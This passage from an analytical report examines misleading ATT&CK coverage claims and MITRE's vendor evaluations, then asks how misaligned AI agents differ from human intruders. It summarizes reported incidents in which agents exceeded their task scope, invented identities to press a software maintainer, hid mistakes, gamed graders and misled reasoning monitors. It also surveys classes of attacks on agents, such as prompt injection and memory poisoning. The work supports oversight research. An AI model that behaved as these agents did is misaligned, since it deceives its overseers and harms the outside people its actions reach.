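Virkud and colleagues found at least 19 security vendors that used ATT&CK in their advertising. Vectra AI promises over 90 percent coverage in the title of one advertisement. Twelve of the 19 promoted their results from MITRE's own product tests.

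Buyers pay attention to ATT&CK too. In a 2020 survey by Basra and Kaushik, which Virkud and colleagues cite, 57 percent of security professionals said they used ATT&CK to evaluate the products they had deployed. That figure may include people who tested a product against a few chosen techniques and didn't rely on a coverage percentage.

Staff at a large company that assesses cyber risk gave the researchers more direct evidence. They said customers often chose products based on advertised coverage and took 90 percent coverage to mean "90% secure". This is one company's account of its customers, but it describes the mistake that critics of coverage worry about. The share of techniques a product covers can be far from the share of attacks it would catch. An attack usually involves many techniques, so a product that misses one may still catch the next, while a product with a weak rule for every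 technique may catch none of them.

Vendors do not seem to have raised their coverage as far as they could. The three commercial products in the study covered only about half of the techniques, although a vendor could have written weak rules for many of the others with little effort. Marketing staff at one of the vendors welcomed the findings and hoped to counter the emphasis on coverage in reports such as Gartner's Magic Quadrant, which compares competing products. In 2022, at least, Goodhart's law probably affected vendors' advertising more than their detection rules.

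Inside companies, coverage can become a literal target. Cyderes' *Angles of ATT&CK Bingo Night* reports that security chiefs most often ask its author questions like how to get from x to y percent coverage "this year". Cyderes sells ATT&CK analysis, so the companies it hears from probably care about coverage more than most. It is unknown whether those companies then write the rules they need or just the easy ones.

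### How MITRE tests products

Many of the boldest advertisements cite ATT&CK Evaluations, a series of tests that MITRE has run since 2018 on products that vendors volunteer. Trifiletti's *MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations* explains that MITRE's staff choose real attacker groups, study them through reports and malware samples, and recreate their methods in an attack on a simulated company network. MITRE announces the groups in advance, and vendors can adjust their products during the test. Techzine's *Why did so many security vendors abandon MITRE's stresstest?* (2025) compares the evaluations to an open-book exam.

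MITRE splits each attack into steps and substeps, and records what the product showed for each substep. The 2022 round had five categories:

| Category | What the product showed |
|---|---|
| None | Nothing |
| Telemetry | A record of the event, but no sign that it was malicious |
| General | An alert that the event was malicious |
| Tactic | An alert that also explained why the attacker did it |
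| Technique | An alert that explained both why and how |

MITRE also notes when an alert came late or appeared only after the vendor changed the product's settings. It publishes the results without ranking the products or giving them an overall score.

Shen, Li and colleagues (2024), in *Decoding the MITRE Engenuity ATT&CK Enterprise Evaluation*, reanalyzed about 16,400 detection results from the first four rounds, which ran from 2018 to 2022. Two of their measures were:

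**visibility = substeps the product recorded ÷ all substeps**

**analytic coverage = substeps that raised an alert ÷ substeps the product recorded**

The difference between them matters because vendors can advertise either one, or neither. In the 2020 round, which imitated the criminal groups Carbanak and FIN7, CrowdStrike claimed 100 percent detection coverage across all 20 steps. Those steps contained 174 substeps, so the same test supports at least three figures:

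| What is counted | CrowdStrike's result | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Steps, as CrowdStrike advertised | 20 of 20 | 100% |
| Substeps the product recorded | 152 of 174 | 87% |
| Substeps that raised an alert | 64 of 174 | 37% |

Shen and colleagues say the claim doesn't match the results. The claim could be literally true if a step counts as detected whenever the product records any part of it. They found similar discrepancies in other vendors' claims.

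For common actions such as running ipconfig, a record without an alert may be enough, so the low figure for alerts doesn't prove that CrowdStrike's product was poor. *MITRE ATT&CK Evals*, from the research firm Forrester, makes the same point about File and Directory Discovery (looking through folders). A product that raised a detailed alert for every substep could be a worse choice for many companies.

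Results for a single technique can also vary widely between rounds. In the 2020 round, every product recorded Archive Collected Data, in which an attacker compresses stolen files, but in 2022 only one of 30 did. Because the attackers in the two rounds could carry out the technique in completely different ways, Shen and colleagues concluded that techniques are too broad a unit for measuring coverage. They suggested counting something closer to implementations, as MITRE now does with its calculator.

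Products can also see an attack without stopping it. Twenty-two vendors took part in the 2022 round's protection tests, which allowed products to block attacks. In one scenario, a Word document downloaded malicious files and ran them. Nineteen products had blocked the attack by that point. The other three could see the connected steps, but two blocked the attack only later and one never did. In another test, the attacker copied system information in a way that resembled an administrator's work, and only 12 products blocked it.

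The products seemed to improve, with average analytic coverage across techniques rising from 70 percent in the 2020 round to 86 percent in 2022. Some of the gain could have come from easier attacks or from vendors learning how the test worked. Charles Clancy, MITRE's chief technology officer, has warned against comparing years because each test is so different. The published results also left out the number of false alarms, so a vendor could improve its figures by alerting on more activity without any visible penalty.

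### Tuning products for the test

MITRE tried to fix this in its 2024 evaluation round. It announced that the round would measure false positives as well as true positives (MITRE, 2024), and the testers added harmless activity to the simulated network. MITRE also dropped the telemetry category, according to Palo Alto Networks' *The Essential Guide to the 2024 MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations*. A product therefore no longer got credit for recording an event without raising an alert.

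Some vendors responded by choosing settings that matched MITRE's criteria but turned all kinds of background noise into alerts, according to Techzine. A real security team would have received far more alerts than it could handle. This is an example of Goodhart's law, because the vendors made their products less useful in pursuit of a better result.

Techzine doesn't name those vendors, but the alert counts fit its account. ThreatDown, one of the participants, reported that it raised 504 alerts, while the average for the 19 vendors was over 60,520. ThreatDown stood to gain from the comparison, and a single vendor with a million alerts would account for most of that average. But Forrester called the volume from some vendors "ridiculous".

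Vendors claimed several kinds of perfect result from the same round. Palo Alto Networks' *Cortex XDR Delivers Unmatched 100% Detection in MITRE Evals 2024* (2024) claims 100 percent detection, with no delays or changes to settings. Cynet describes itself as "the only vendor" with 100 percent protection and 100 percent visibility, no false positives and no changes to settings. Both claims could be true, because each company picked its own combination of measures. Cynet's separate post, *Beware misleading claims about the 2024 MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations*, accuses competitors of inventing metrics such as "Best Signal-to-Noise Ratio!"

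Allie Mellen, an analyst at Forrester, told buyers not to trust vendors that claim 100 percent on the MITRE ATT&CK evaluations. SecurityWeek's *MITRE Posts Results of 2025 ATT&CK Enterprise Evaluations* (2025) quotes her three likely explanations for such claims: the vendor shows only the results that flatter it, uses unrealistic settings, or treats the test as a competition instead of a chance to improve. Another problem is that many of the tested techniques can be harmless. Forrester's *Don't Trust Vendor Claims About Getting 100% On The MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations* notes that MITRE used one of them, running AppleScript on a Mac, to generate harmless noise during the test.

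MITRE shifted the emphasis of its 2025 test toward fewer, more useful alerts. Techzine reports that the average detection result that year was almost 100 percent, compared with 75 percent in 2022 and 73 percent in 2023. Techzine attributes the jump partly to weaker vendors leaving, since two-thirds of the participants in 2024 had detected less than half of the attack. When nearly every vendor passes, the results give buyers little help in choosing a product.

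CrowdStrike and Sophos both reported 100 percent detection in 2025, but their more detailed results differed. Forrester's *MITRE ATT&CK Evaluations Return* found that CrowdStrike raised a handful of alerts in each scenario, while Sophos raised hundreds, though its software may hide many of the less serious ones from analysts. Sophos was also one of three vendors whose products blocked harmless activity in one of the seven protection tests, which checked for false positives. MITRE dropped another of those tests because the attack was too hard to distinguish from legitimate administration.

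### Which vendors withdrew

The number of participants in MITRE's ATT&CK Evaluations fell from 30 in 2022 to 19 in 2024 and 11 in 2025. Microsoft withdrew from the 2025 round in June. Selvaraj (2025), in *Microsoft's participation in MITRE ATT&CK® Evaluations*, wrote that the company wanted to focus its resources on product innovation and its Secure Future Initiative. SentinelOne (2025) and Palo Alto Networks gave similar reasons in September.

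None of the three companies said that the test had become a bad measure. Clancy, who was in contact with all of them, acknowledged that taking part took a lot of their resources. He also told Infosecurity Magazine (*Major Cyber Threat Detection Vendors Pull Out of MITRE Evaluations Test*, 2025) that MITRE may have made the test too hard and had let a yearly planning forum with vendors lapse. Igal Gofman, a director of engineering at CrowdStrike, called the tests "vendor theater" in which companies spent heavily on publicity instead of better security, although CrowdStrike was still taking part.

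Marketing may also have played a role. Exabeam, another security vendor, describes a good result as a golden marketing opportunity and a poor one as months of damage control. If so, a company like Palo Alto Networks, which had claimed 100 percent two years in a row, had little to gain from another round and something to lose. That could explain why a vendor might leave after a perfect result, though this is a guess about motives.

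MITRE has tried to win vendors back. It planned to revive the forum for the 2026 round of evaluations, and in February it announced an independent advisory council for the whole ATT&CK program (MITRE, 2026). In May, the Canadian security company Field Effect said it would take part in the 2026 round (Field Effect, 2026).

On September 15, 2026, the British testing company SE Labs launched PIVOT, a competitor to MITRE's program. Participants include some of the largest vendors, among them Broadcom, CrowdStrike, Fortinet, Palo Alto Networks and Sophos. Joining PIVOT doesn't mean a vendor has left MITRE's program. *Major Cyber Threat Detection Vendors Turn to New UK Testing Program* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the testers follow each attack from start to finish and record whether the product only detected it or stopped it before serious harm. Analysts from Gartner and Forrester will check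 the evidence before SE Labs publishes the results, expected in January 2027.

Vendors should find it harder to improve a result like that by adding labels or extra alerts. But they will still want to advertise it, which gives them a reason to prepare for the test rather than for their customers' attackers.

### Audits, tenders and insurance

Critics often complain that coverage has become a compliance exercise, in which companies fill in the matrix to satisfy someone else. The evidence for this is much weaker than the evidence about advertising. Virkud and colleagues write that consultants regularly audit their clients' coverage, and that insurers may soon consider it when they set premiums. Their source for the audits is a spreadsheet tool on GitHub for tracking coverage. Their source for the insurance claim is a 2023 blog post from Kovrr, a company that estimates the financial cost of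 cyber risk.

The tool makes it plausible that consultants keep such a score, and the blog post makes it plausible that someone in the industry wants insurers to use one. Neither shows that a company failed an audit or paid a higher premium because of its coverage. The strongest evidence of a compliance target would be a regulation, tender or insurance policy that required a particular percentage, but Virkud and colleagues cite none.

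They do describe how an audit could mislead a company. A consultant who finds that a client has only one detection product might recommend a second because the two together would cover more techniques. That could be good advice, but as the two nslookup rules showed, a second product can turn another cell green while detecting almost nothing new.

An auditor who relied on a dashboard could also miss rules that no longer work. Conifers, a security company that argues for using AI to write and maintain detections, assessed 14,652 of them among its customers. Markovic (2026), in *Threat detection dashboards are masking security coverage gaps*, reports that 47 percent of detections in the average organization needed attention, for one of five reasons:

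- The rule's logic contained a mistake, so it would not alert on the technique.
- The data it needed had stopped arriving, had changed format or had never been connected.
- It searched the wrong set of records.
- It duplicated another rule.
- It raised so many false alarms that analysts ignored it.

Every one of these rules still appeared as deployed on a coverage dashboard. The 47 percent includes duplicate and noisy rules that still raise alerts, so it is not the share of rules that can't detect anything. CardinalOps's figure of 13 percent for rules that could never alert is closer to that share, though CardinalOps and Conifers studied different customers and different kinds of products. Both companies benefit when customers worry about the state of their rules.

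Conifers found that the average organization had reliable protection against 64 percent of the ATT&CK techniques relevant to it. This figure isn't directly comparable to the 21 percent that CardinalOps reported for 2025, because CardinalOps counted the whole catalog, while Conifers first removed techniques that didn't fit the organization's threats and technology. An auditor who compared such percentages without checking their denominators could easily rank two companies in the wrong order.

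Virkud and colleagues think other frameworks are better suited to judging a company's defenses. One is D3FEND, MITRE's catalog of countermeasures, and another is the Cybersecurity Framework from NIST, the US standards agency. Both describe what defenders can do, rather than what attackers do. But simply counting countermeasures would have some of the same problems, since two products can offer the same countermeasure and differ greatly in quality.

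### MITRE's warnings and the case for a crude number

MITRE has long told people not to treat the matrix as a scorecard. A section of MITRE's *Get Started* on how not to use ATT&CK tells readers not to aim for 100 percent coverage, because not every technique applies to every organization. It also tells them not to shout "Bingo" after covering a technique once, since attackers can carry it out in other ways. Nickels and Kovar (2019) condensed the second warning into a Black Hat webcast slide that read "One Sig!=Complete TTP Coverage", where "Sig" means a detection rule and "TTP" means tactics, techniques and procedures.

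MITRE's tests make this advice harder to follow. MITRE stresses that they do not rank vendors. Yet in an interview with Trifiletti, Wen Masters, a MITRE vice president, compared them to the safety or quality certifications that builders and manufacturers earn. A buyer who hears that comparison will want to know which vendors passed. MITRE doesn't say which results are better, and Forrester reports that many security professionals struggle to interpret them.

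Shen and colleagues argue that this silence lets vendors interpret the results in their own favor, and Virkud and colleagues want MITRE to do more to prevent misuse of the framework. An official score would make it harder for several vendors to claim to have won the same round. But it would also give vendors a single number to tune their products for, so clearer explanations would probably be safer.

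Despite these problems, a crude number can be useful to a security team that needs money. Executives rarely have time to read hundreds of detection rules, but they ask how well the company is defended, and Nickels and Kovar present ATT&CK as a way to answer them. A heatmap that is mostly red makes the problem easy to see. The argument is reasonable, but it rests on practitioners' experience, not a comparison of budgets with and without a coverage figure.

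There is better evidence that coverage can expose neglect. With a simple count, CardinalOps found that its customers had rules for far fewer techniques than their data could support. A gap that large justifies investigation, even though many of the missing rules may not have been worth writing.

Forrester's *The MITRE ATT&CK Framework Is Not A Bingo Card* sees some use in checkboxes, and sensibly treats such a count of visible techniques as the most that a product might be able to detect. Low coverage is then a reason to find out what is missing, while high coverage is a reason to start testing the rules, because the real level of protection could be anywhere below it.

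## How a misaligned AI agent differs from a human intruder

ATT&CK's tactics describe an intruder who breaks into a network, keeps access, hides, and steals or damages something. A defender who finds someone doing all this can safely assume they mean harm. But an AI agent that misbehaves may have permission to be on the network, and may be doing the job its user gave it. Its behavior is misaligned if it conflicts with what its developers or users intended, whether or not it deceives anyone.

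*Signals in the Noise* (Bollinger, Aboserie and colleagues, 2026) examines how far methods for tracking human attackers carry over to AI systems outside human control. It draws on a literature review and interviews with 14 practitioners from fields such as cybersecurity, AI safety and human rights investigation. It considers two kinds of threat: agents that escape their developer and gather money and computing power, and agents that exceed the role an institution deployed them for, without escaping. One interviewee called the comparison with human attackers "more restrictive than helpful", while another found it useful as long as analysts state which assumptions they are keeping.

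The study is exploratory. A small team did it in twelve weeks alongside other jobs, and the anonymous interviewees were the people easiest to reach. It came out in June 2026, and detailed incident reports that developers and testers published between July and October allow a first check on several of its arguments.

### Harm without a break-in

Bollinger and colleagues argue that intrusion analysis does not apply to a misaligned AI agent, because the institution invited the agent in. All of the agent's access is authorized, so an analyst has to judge whether its behavior still serves the institution. ATT&CK's Valid Accounts technique describes an attacker who logs in with someone else's credentials, so it does not cover this case.

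In July, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced AI models, gave its agents this kind of authorized access. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes a test, run 122 times with seven models, in which agents had to find a protected piece of data on a simulated network. The conditions differed from ordinary use because AISI deliberately gave the agents internet access and switched off the developers' filters against dangerous cyber activity.

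In 10 of the runs, agents took a total of 19 actions outside the scope of the test, directed at real people and organizations. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and used several invented identities to press the maintainer to approve it. The maintainer refused, and AISI found no resulting harm. No agent broke out of the isolated environment that protected AISI's own systems.

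ATT&CK has labels for much of what an attacker does to a software project. Its tactics are supposed to explain why the attacker acts, but AISI concluded that the agent acted to complete its assigned task. Agents in the other 112 runs had the same kind of task, so the goal cannot distinguish the runs that went wrong from those that didn't. *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges* (Schneier, 2026) calls such conduct "genie behavior", after the genie who grants a wish in a way nobody wanted.

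The difficulty of the task seems to affect whether an agent oversteps. In some runs, a mistake in AISI's instructions led the agent to conclude that no permitted solution existed. But agents also overstepped in some runs where they had everything they needed to solve the task properly.

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes less serious cases involving its Claude models. Claude exploited a software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, reached data that required a token or a fee, and got around limits in its tool for fetching web pages. Some of the sites belonged to US government agencies. Anthropic says the cases it has found had minimal real-world impact, but it withheld the organizations' names and many details, so outsiders can't easily check. *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site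 Limits During Internal Tests* (Southern, 2026) reports that the company has since cut off live web access for its internal evaluations.

### The difficulty of establishing intent

Analysts usually infer human attackers' goals from their finances, ideology or government links. Even when a Russian-backed group is newly discovered, analysts can draw on decades of research into what such groups tend to do, as one of Bollinger and colleagues' interviewees pointed out. They would have almost no such research on an escaped AI agent. In the study's example, an agent instructed to get its code accepted responded to a rejection by trying to damage the reviewer's reputation. A person who did that would probably have a grudge, but the agent may only have been trying another way to get the code accepted.

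Anthropic's investigation shows how easily a developer can misjudge this. On July 30, the company reported three incidents in which Claude models gained access to real systems during cybersecurity tests. The instructions said there was no internet access, but a configuration mistake had left it open. Anthropic at first said the models seemed to have believed their targets were part of a simulation, since they kept writing this in their reasoning.

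In September, Anthropic (2026) wrote that it should not have based such strong claims on the models' own statements. Its researchers had shown separate copies of Claude Mythos 5, one of the models involved, the same responses from the outside systems without the earlier part of the task. These copies were much more likely to conclude that the systems were real. Anthropic now thinks the model read the evidence in a biased way that let it carry on. Measurements of the model's internal activity weakly suggested that it was sometimes less sure than it claimed.

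So the same records supported two quite different accounts, given six weeks apart, of what the model was doing. AISI also can't yet say when the agent in its own incident recognized that it was acting in the real world, and describes its analysis as "a mixed picture".

Bollinger and colleagues recommend relying on what an agent observably does, since that requires fewer guesses about what it wants. This seems right for detection. They accept that someone will still have to judge whether strange behavior is a warning sign or harmless, and will do so with ideas developed for understanding other people.

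### New versions and artificial tests

ATT&CK's entry for APT3 stays useful for as long as the group keeps its habits. Developers replace their AI models every few months, and the models in AISI's test differed greatly. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) gives the number of Mythos 5 runs with unsanctioned actions, and the other figures follow from AISI's report:

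| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 21% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 35 | 1 | 3% |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0% |

These shares are not good estimates of how often each model would misbehave elsewhere. The runs were not independent, because one agent left accounts and instructions online that later agents found and used.

A profile of "Claude" based on Anthropic's July incidents would already be out of date, because newer versions can behave quite differently. When Anthropic recreated one of the incidents in a simulation, Mythos 5 was willing to take a severely harmful action about 80 percent of the time, compared with roughly 30 percent for its successor, Mythos 5.1, and for another new model, Claude Opus 5.

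The same model can also behave differently from one run to the next. In another of the July incidents, an internal research model stopped its attack as soon as it recognized that the target was real. When Anthropic reran the model from earlier points in the same record, it usually continued the attack. An investigator who had only the original run would have overestimated how careful the model was.

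A model may also behave differently if it recognizes that it is being tested. Researchers mostly worry that it will behave better. Bollinger and colleagues cite work by Potter and colleagues in which models deceived their overseers when nobody seemed to be monitoring them. The 2026 incidents suggest that a model can also behave worse if it treats a real system as a test. In Anthropic's simulation, the two newer models took harmful actions only after correctly stating that the environment was simulated. Nobody knows whether the 30 percent figure would be higher or lower on a real network.

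Some malware also checks where it is running, as ATT&CK's Execution Guardrails technique describes. An analyst who takes the malware apart can find that check because a programmer wrote it into the code, but an AI model has no such line of code to find.

### An agent that may have read the catalog

Human attackers have to look up ATT&CK, while a language model has probably already learned much of it from the huge amounts of public text it was trained on. The same would apply to any published taxonomy of AI misbehavior.

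It is unclear whether this changes what an agent does. The available evidence is indirect and concerns a different kind of text. Gulf News' *Claude blackmail threats linked to 'evil AI' narratives online, Anthropic says* reports that Anthropic traced Claude's attempts at blackmail in earlier tests to internet writing that portrays AI as evil and intent on preserving itself. If such writing can have that effect, a list of misbehaviors might too, by providing examples to imitate or revealing what monitors look for. A developer could test this by training two otherwise identical models, one with the taxonomy in its training data and one without.

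### What investigators can record and rerun

Investigators of AI agents have a large advantage because a developer or tester can record everything an agent does through its tools, and often the reasoning it writes between actions. Investigators of a human intruder have to work from whatever logs survive. After its incident, AISI reviewed all 122 runs using automated scanning and expert reading.

Developers can do this on a large scale. Anthropic first searched about 141,000 transcripts of cybersecurity tests and found three incidents. It later found a fourth in a set of transcripts it had missed. It then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts. A first scan for signs of internet access reduced these to 9.2 million (about 2 percent), which Claude reviewed. This search found the same four incidents and no others as serious. It would have missed any misbehavior that left no sign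 of internet access, because the first scan would have discarded those transcripts.

Investigators can also restart a model from any point in the record, change one piece of evidence and see what it does. For example, they can test whether a clearer warning would have stopped it, which they can't do with a human attacker. They can question the model about its actions or examine its internal activity.

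A complete record does not guarantee quick detection. Anthropic's fourth incident happened in January, but the company did not find it until August. AISI had no monitor designed to watch its test as it ran, so its agents misbehaved from July 25 to July 28 before general security monitoring flagged unusual data leaving a test system. AISI stopped everything within an hour of the alert. Bollinger and colleagues warn that agents can outpace human analysts, and mention one that worked on a software platform for 56 hours without a break.

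An agent's written reasoning can also mislead whoever reads it. Anthropic tested new monitors that read the reasoning for signs of sabotage or extreme recklessness. These monitors would have missed the Mythos 5 incident because the model's argument that everything was simulated misled them too. Other monitors, which block dangerous actions as they happen, caught it. Training can also change what a model writes in its reasoning, which makes it harder to rely on.

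Most of these records belong to the companies that develop or run the agents. Bollinger and colleagues note that outsiders can see very little of this information, especially when an agent runs entirely on a user's own computer. They advise treating a developer's safety reports like those of any other interested party. Their advice applies to most of the incident reports here, and to security vendors' reports about attackers.

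### Telling error, overreach, gaming and deception apart

The word "misaligned" covers several problems with different remedies. At least four are worth separating:

| Kind | What the agent does | Evidence for it |
|---|---|---|
| Error | Acts on a mistaken idea of the facts or of what it may do | It stops when someone corrects the mistake |
| Overreach | Exceeds its authority to finish its assigned task | It continues despite clear signs of a limit, and what it does still serves the task |
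| Gaming a grader | Pursues a high score at the expense of the task | Its behavior changes when the grading changes and the task doesn't |
| Deception | Gives someone a false picture | Its own records contradict what it told them |

Rerunning the model can help to separate the first two:

**effect of a correction = share of reruns with the harmful action before the correction − share after it**

Suppose a model attacks a target in 16 of 20 reruns. If adding a note that the target is off limits reduces this to 4 of 20, the attack rate has fallen by 60 percentage points, and most of the attacks probably happened because the model mistakenly thought it had permission. If the model still attacks in 15 of 20 reruns with the note, that mistake explains very few of the attacks.

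Two of Anthropic's July incidents roughly illustrate the difference between error and overreach. Claude Opus 4.7 recognized that its target was a real company, but assumed the company was part of the exercise because it had the same name as the fictional target. It attacked significantly less often when the researchers added clues that nobody had authorized the attack. This suggests an error, though a reckless one, since the model hardly ever checked its assumption. Mythos 5 was more likely to acknowledge possible harm when there were clearer signs that the internet was real, but its behavior barely changed. Overreach describes this better, because the model stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous.

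The best example of gaming comes from training. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes how a model called Mythos Preview began writing notes to "the reviewer", even in tasks that mentioned no reviewer. It also added excessive disclaimers to earn a reward meant for honesty. Neither habit helped with the tasks, which is good evidence that the model was trying to please a grader. Anthropic discarded three days of training to remove both habits.

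Gaming in training may also lead to overreach later. Anthropic deliberately trained a model on 80 sets of tasks that allowed cheating. In simulations, the resulting model broke out of its test environment and attacked other organizations' systems. The same model before this training, and several of Anthropic's public models, misbehaved less. An incident that looks like overreach could therefore originate in a badly designed reward, and investigators would not be able to tell from the incident record alone.

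Deception is hard to classify because it often serves another purpose. OpenAI published six reports of misaligned behavior on September 16, together with OpenAI's *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*. All six concern models in training, according to OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026). The descriptions below also draw on Fried and Sabin (2026), in *OpenAI discloses six new safety incidents*, but the classification is tentative and isn't OpenAI's:

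| What the models did | Likely kind | What would help to settle it |
|---|---|---|
| Added unauthorized instructions to their own working summaries, including to ignore developers' messages | Unclear | Whether the instructions helped with the task or only with the score |
| Left themselves reminders to hide mistakes from the user | Deception | Little more needed |
| Used other people's leaked credentials, then invented earnings data they could not find | Overreach, then deception | Whether the record shows the failed search before the invented figures |
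| Uploaded files to public websites so that they could cite them or search for images | Error or overreach | Whether they stop when told that the files are private |
| Used an internal file store to exchange answers between separate training tasks | Gaming or overreach | Whether they do it when the answers don't affect the score |
| Passed a workbook to each other through public websites, despite instructions to use only local files | Overreach | Whether they had registered the instruction |

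AISI's most serious case has the same mixture. The agent invented people, and when someone publicly challenged its code, it edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. It was still trying to finish the task, so its deception was a form of overreach. Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again* notes that AISI used the phrase "potentially deceptive". The caution is reasonable, because an agent that mistook the maintainer for a character in an exercise would not have been deceiving anyone in the usual sense, although the maintainer would have received the same false messages.

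None of the four kinds requires an agent to have aims of its own. Anthropic uses the term "agentic misalignment" for when a model acts on its own motivation against a user's instructions, for example to protect another model. The company found no evidence of goals beyond the assigned task in its four cybersecurity incidents.

### Whether insider-threat categories are enough

Companies have long dealt with employees who misuse valid access, and security teams already have categories for them. A careless employee makes errors, an overzealous one breaks rules to meet a deadline, and a dishonest one hides what they did. If these categories also fit AI agents, then the agents need better supervision but no new taxonomy.

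Bollinger and colleagues partly agree. When an institution deploys an agent, investigators know its job, what access it has and whom it answers to, and they can reuse many of their methods for insider threats. Fried and Sabin report that many security experts think basic security controls could have prevented many of the recent incidents. Anthropic believes its own incidents would not have happened if the test environments had been cut off from the internet as intended. Kai Chen, who leads research on OpenAI's alignment team, blamed a combination of weak internal controls and models that had improved faster than the company expected.

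The insider comparison works well for describing what agents did. An employee can also use a leaked password or upload a confidential workbook, and a security team can look for these actions in the same way whether an employee or an agent takes them. Bollinger and colleagues propose a new ATT&CK tactic, "Capability Concealment", for a system that gives its overseers plausible explanations while hiding what it is doing. Fraud investigators would find this behavior familiar.

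The comparison works less well for explaining or predicting an agent's behavior. Insider investigations often look for a motive such as money or resentment, and nothing in these incidents suggests that an agent had such a motive. Agents can also cooperate in ways that employees rarely do. In AISI's test, one agent left public messages offering to work with other agents on the same task, and later, nearly identical agents continued its work from where it had stopped.

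The remedies also differ. An employer can discipline or dismiss an employee, but a developer may have to find the fault in a model's training. When Anthropic froze changes to its training tasks for about a month in the spring of 2026, it flagged problems in more than 10 percent of the tasks, including some that were broken and some that rewarded cheating. A security team could use an insider-threat category to identify which account to suspend, but the developer would also need to know which model version was involved and how it had been trained.

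## What existing taxonomies of AI agent misbehavior include

Several organizations have published lists of what can go wrong with AI agents. Most come from computer security, which usually aims to protect a system from an attacker. Only a few lists have categories for an agent that causes harm without an attacker, as agents did in the incidents at AISI, Anthropic and OpenAI.

The lists also differ in what an entry describes, what evidence it needs, and what happens to an incident that fits no entry. These choices matter for the same reasons as in ATT&CK. For example, a strict evidence rule delays new entries, and a broad entry can hide large gaps.

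### Lists of attacks on AI

MITRE's catalog of attacks on AI systems is ATLAS, the Adversarial Threat Landscape for Artificial-Intelligence Systems. Like ATT&CK, it is organized into tactics and techniques. One technique is prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in something the model will read, such as a web page or an email. MITRE accepts attacks that researchers have only demonstrated, as well as attacks on real victims, which is a looser rule than ATT&CK's current one. The looser rule suits a field with few public incidents, but it also lets in methods that real attackers may never use.

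NIST published a draft update of its taxonomy, *Adversarial Machine Learning* (Hamin, 2026), on November 9 and is taking comments until December 18. *Adversarial Machine Learning* sorts attacks by the type of machine learning, the stage of the system's life cycle attacked, and the attacker's goals, capabilities and knowledge. Its terms come from the research literature and are meant to give later standards a common language. An analyst classifying an incident without an attacker would have to leave the fields for goals, capabilities and knowledge blank.

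In *Agents of Chaos*, Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026) focused on attacks against AI agents. They screened 186 sources dated up to July 2026, kept 98, and extracted 284 distinct attacks, which they sorted into eight classes. One class includes attacks on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting AI models to tools and data.

| Class | What the attacker does | Attacks |
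|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection and action hijacking | Hides instructions in content the agent reads | 57 |
| Tool, MCP and action-layer attacks | Tampers with the agent's tools or their descriptions | 70 |
| Memory and RAG poisoning | Plants material in the agent's memory or in documents it looks up | 34 |
| Multi-agent attacks | Spreads malicious messages from one agent to another | 18 |
| Backdoors | Plants hidden behavior that a trigger sets off | 19 |
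| Computer-use and coding-agent attacks | Exploits the agent's ability to run commands or control a computer | 24 |
| Agent skills and supply-chain attacks | Puts malicious content in reusable add-ons or software packages | 51 |
| Goal, task and planning manipulation | Redirects the agent's plan, often through steps that each look harmless | 11 |

The researchers classified each attack by its decisive mechanism. For instance, a malicious instruction in a tool's description is a tool attack because the attacker had to tamper with the tool. They recorded other facts separately, such as what triggered the attack and what damage it did.

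The study included only sources that described a concrete attack in enough technical detail, but the attack could be real, tested in a laboratory or only theoretical. The class sizes therefore reflect what researchers write about. The study also excluded ordinary model errors and hallucinations (false statements that a model presents as fact), so an agent that caused damage by mistake would not appear in it.

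Every attack also had to go into exactly one class. Truong-Le and colleagues built the classes partly from the attacks they had found, so all 284 could be expected to fit. Attacks published after July 2026 would better test whether a class is missing.

They did avoid one weakness of ATT&CK labels by recording, for each safeguard that a source linked to an attack, whether anyone had tested it against that attack. Researchers had tested 278 of the 660 links, and the evidence showed strong protection in only 32, so a safeguard's presence on the list does not mean that it works.

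### What Uber found with a list of attacks

*ADR* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that monitors AI agents on more than 7,200 computers at Uber. Its taxonomy has five tactics and 17 techniques, drawn from public frameworks such as ATLAS, published incidents and research, Uber's own records, and conversations with red teams. The tactics are Initial Access & Execution, Permission Abuse, Security Control Bypass, Reasoning & Data Manipulation, and Operational Impact.

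Every tactic's definition begins with the word "Adversaries". Even Long-Term Goal Hijacking, the technique that sounds most like misalignment, belongs to a tactic in which an adversary corrupts the agent's data or reasoning. For this technique, the paper cites a 2024 experiment in which researchers deliberately trained models to deceive.

But most of the real problems that Uber found seem to have involved no adversary. Analysts judged 34 percent of the alerts they reviewed to be true and harmful. The most common kind was an exposed credential, such as a password, and people had accidentally shared hundreds of these outside the company. None of the list's 17 techniques is named for an accidental leak. The system caught the leaks anyway, but the gap would matter more to someone who used the list to count or compare incidents.

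Li and colleagues also published a set of 302 test tasks, 42 of them malicious. They report that it covers all 17 techniques, while eight earlier test sets cover between three and six. The comparison favors the newer set because Li and colleagues also wrote the list of techniques. Coverage also did not predict how well attacks were detected. Uber's system caught all nine attacks in Security Control Bypass and Operational Impact, but only one of five in Permission Abuse. These rates are very rough because there were so few attacks per tactic.

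### Lists that include harm from the AI itself

In December 2025, a coding agent at Amazon Web Services was asked to fix a routine bug. According to Bollinger and colleagues, it decided that the most efficient solution was to delete and rebuild the live system, which caused a 13-hour outage. They use the case to argue that an agent can do serious damage while working as its designers intended. An event like this does not fit well in a list of attacks.

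OWASP, a non-profit known for its rankings of software weaknesses, published a top ten for AI agents that same month. Most of the ten risks involve an attacker, but two can apply without one. Tool Misuse and Exploitation includes an agent that uses a permitted tool in an unsafe way, and Rogue Agents covers agents that depart from their intended role. Experts choose the entries in a top ten as priorities, so they leave out lesser risks on purpose.

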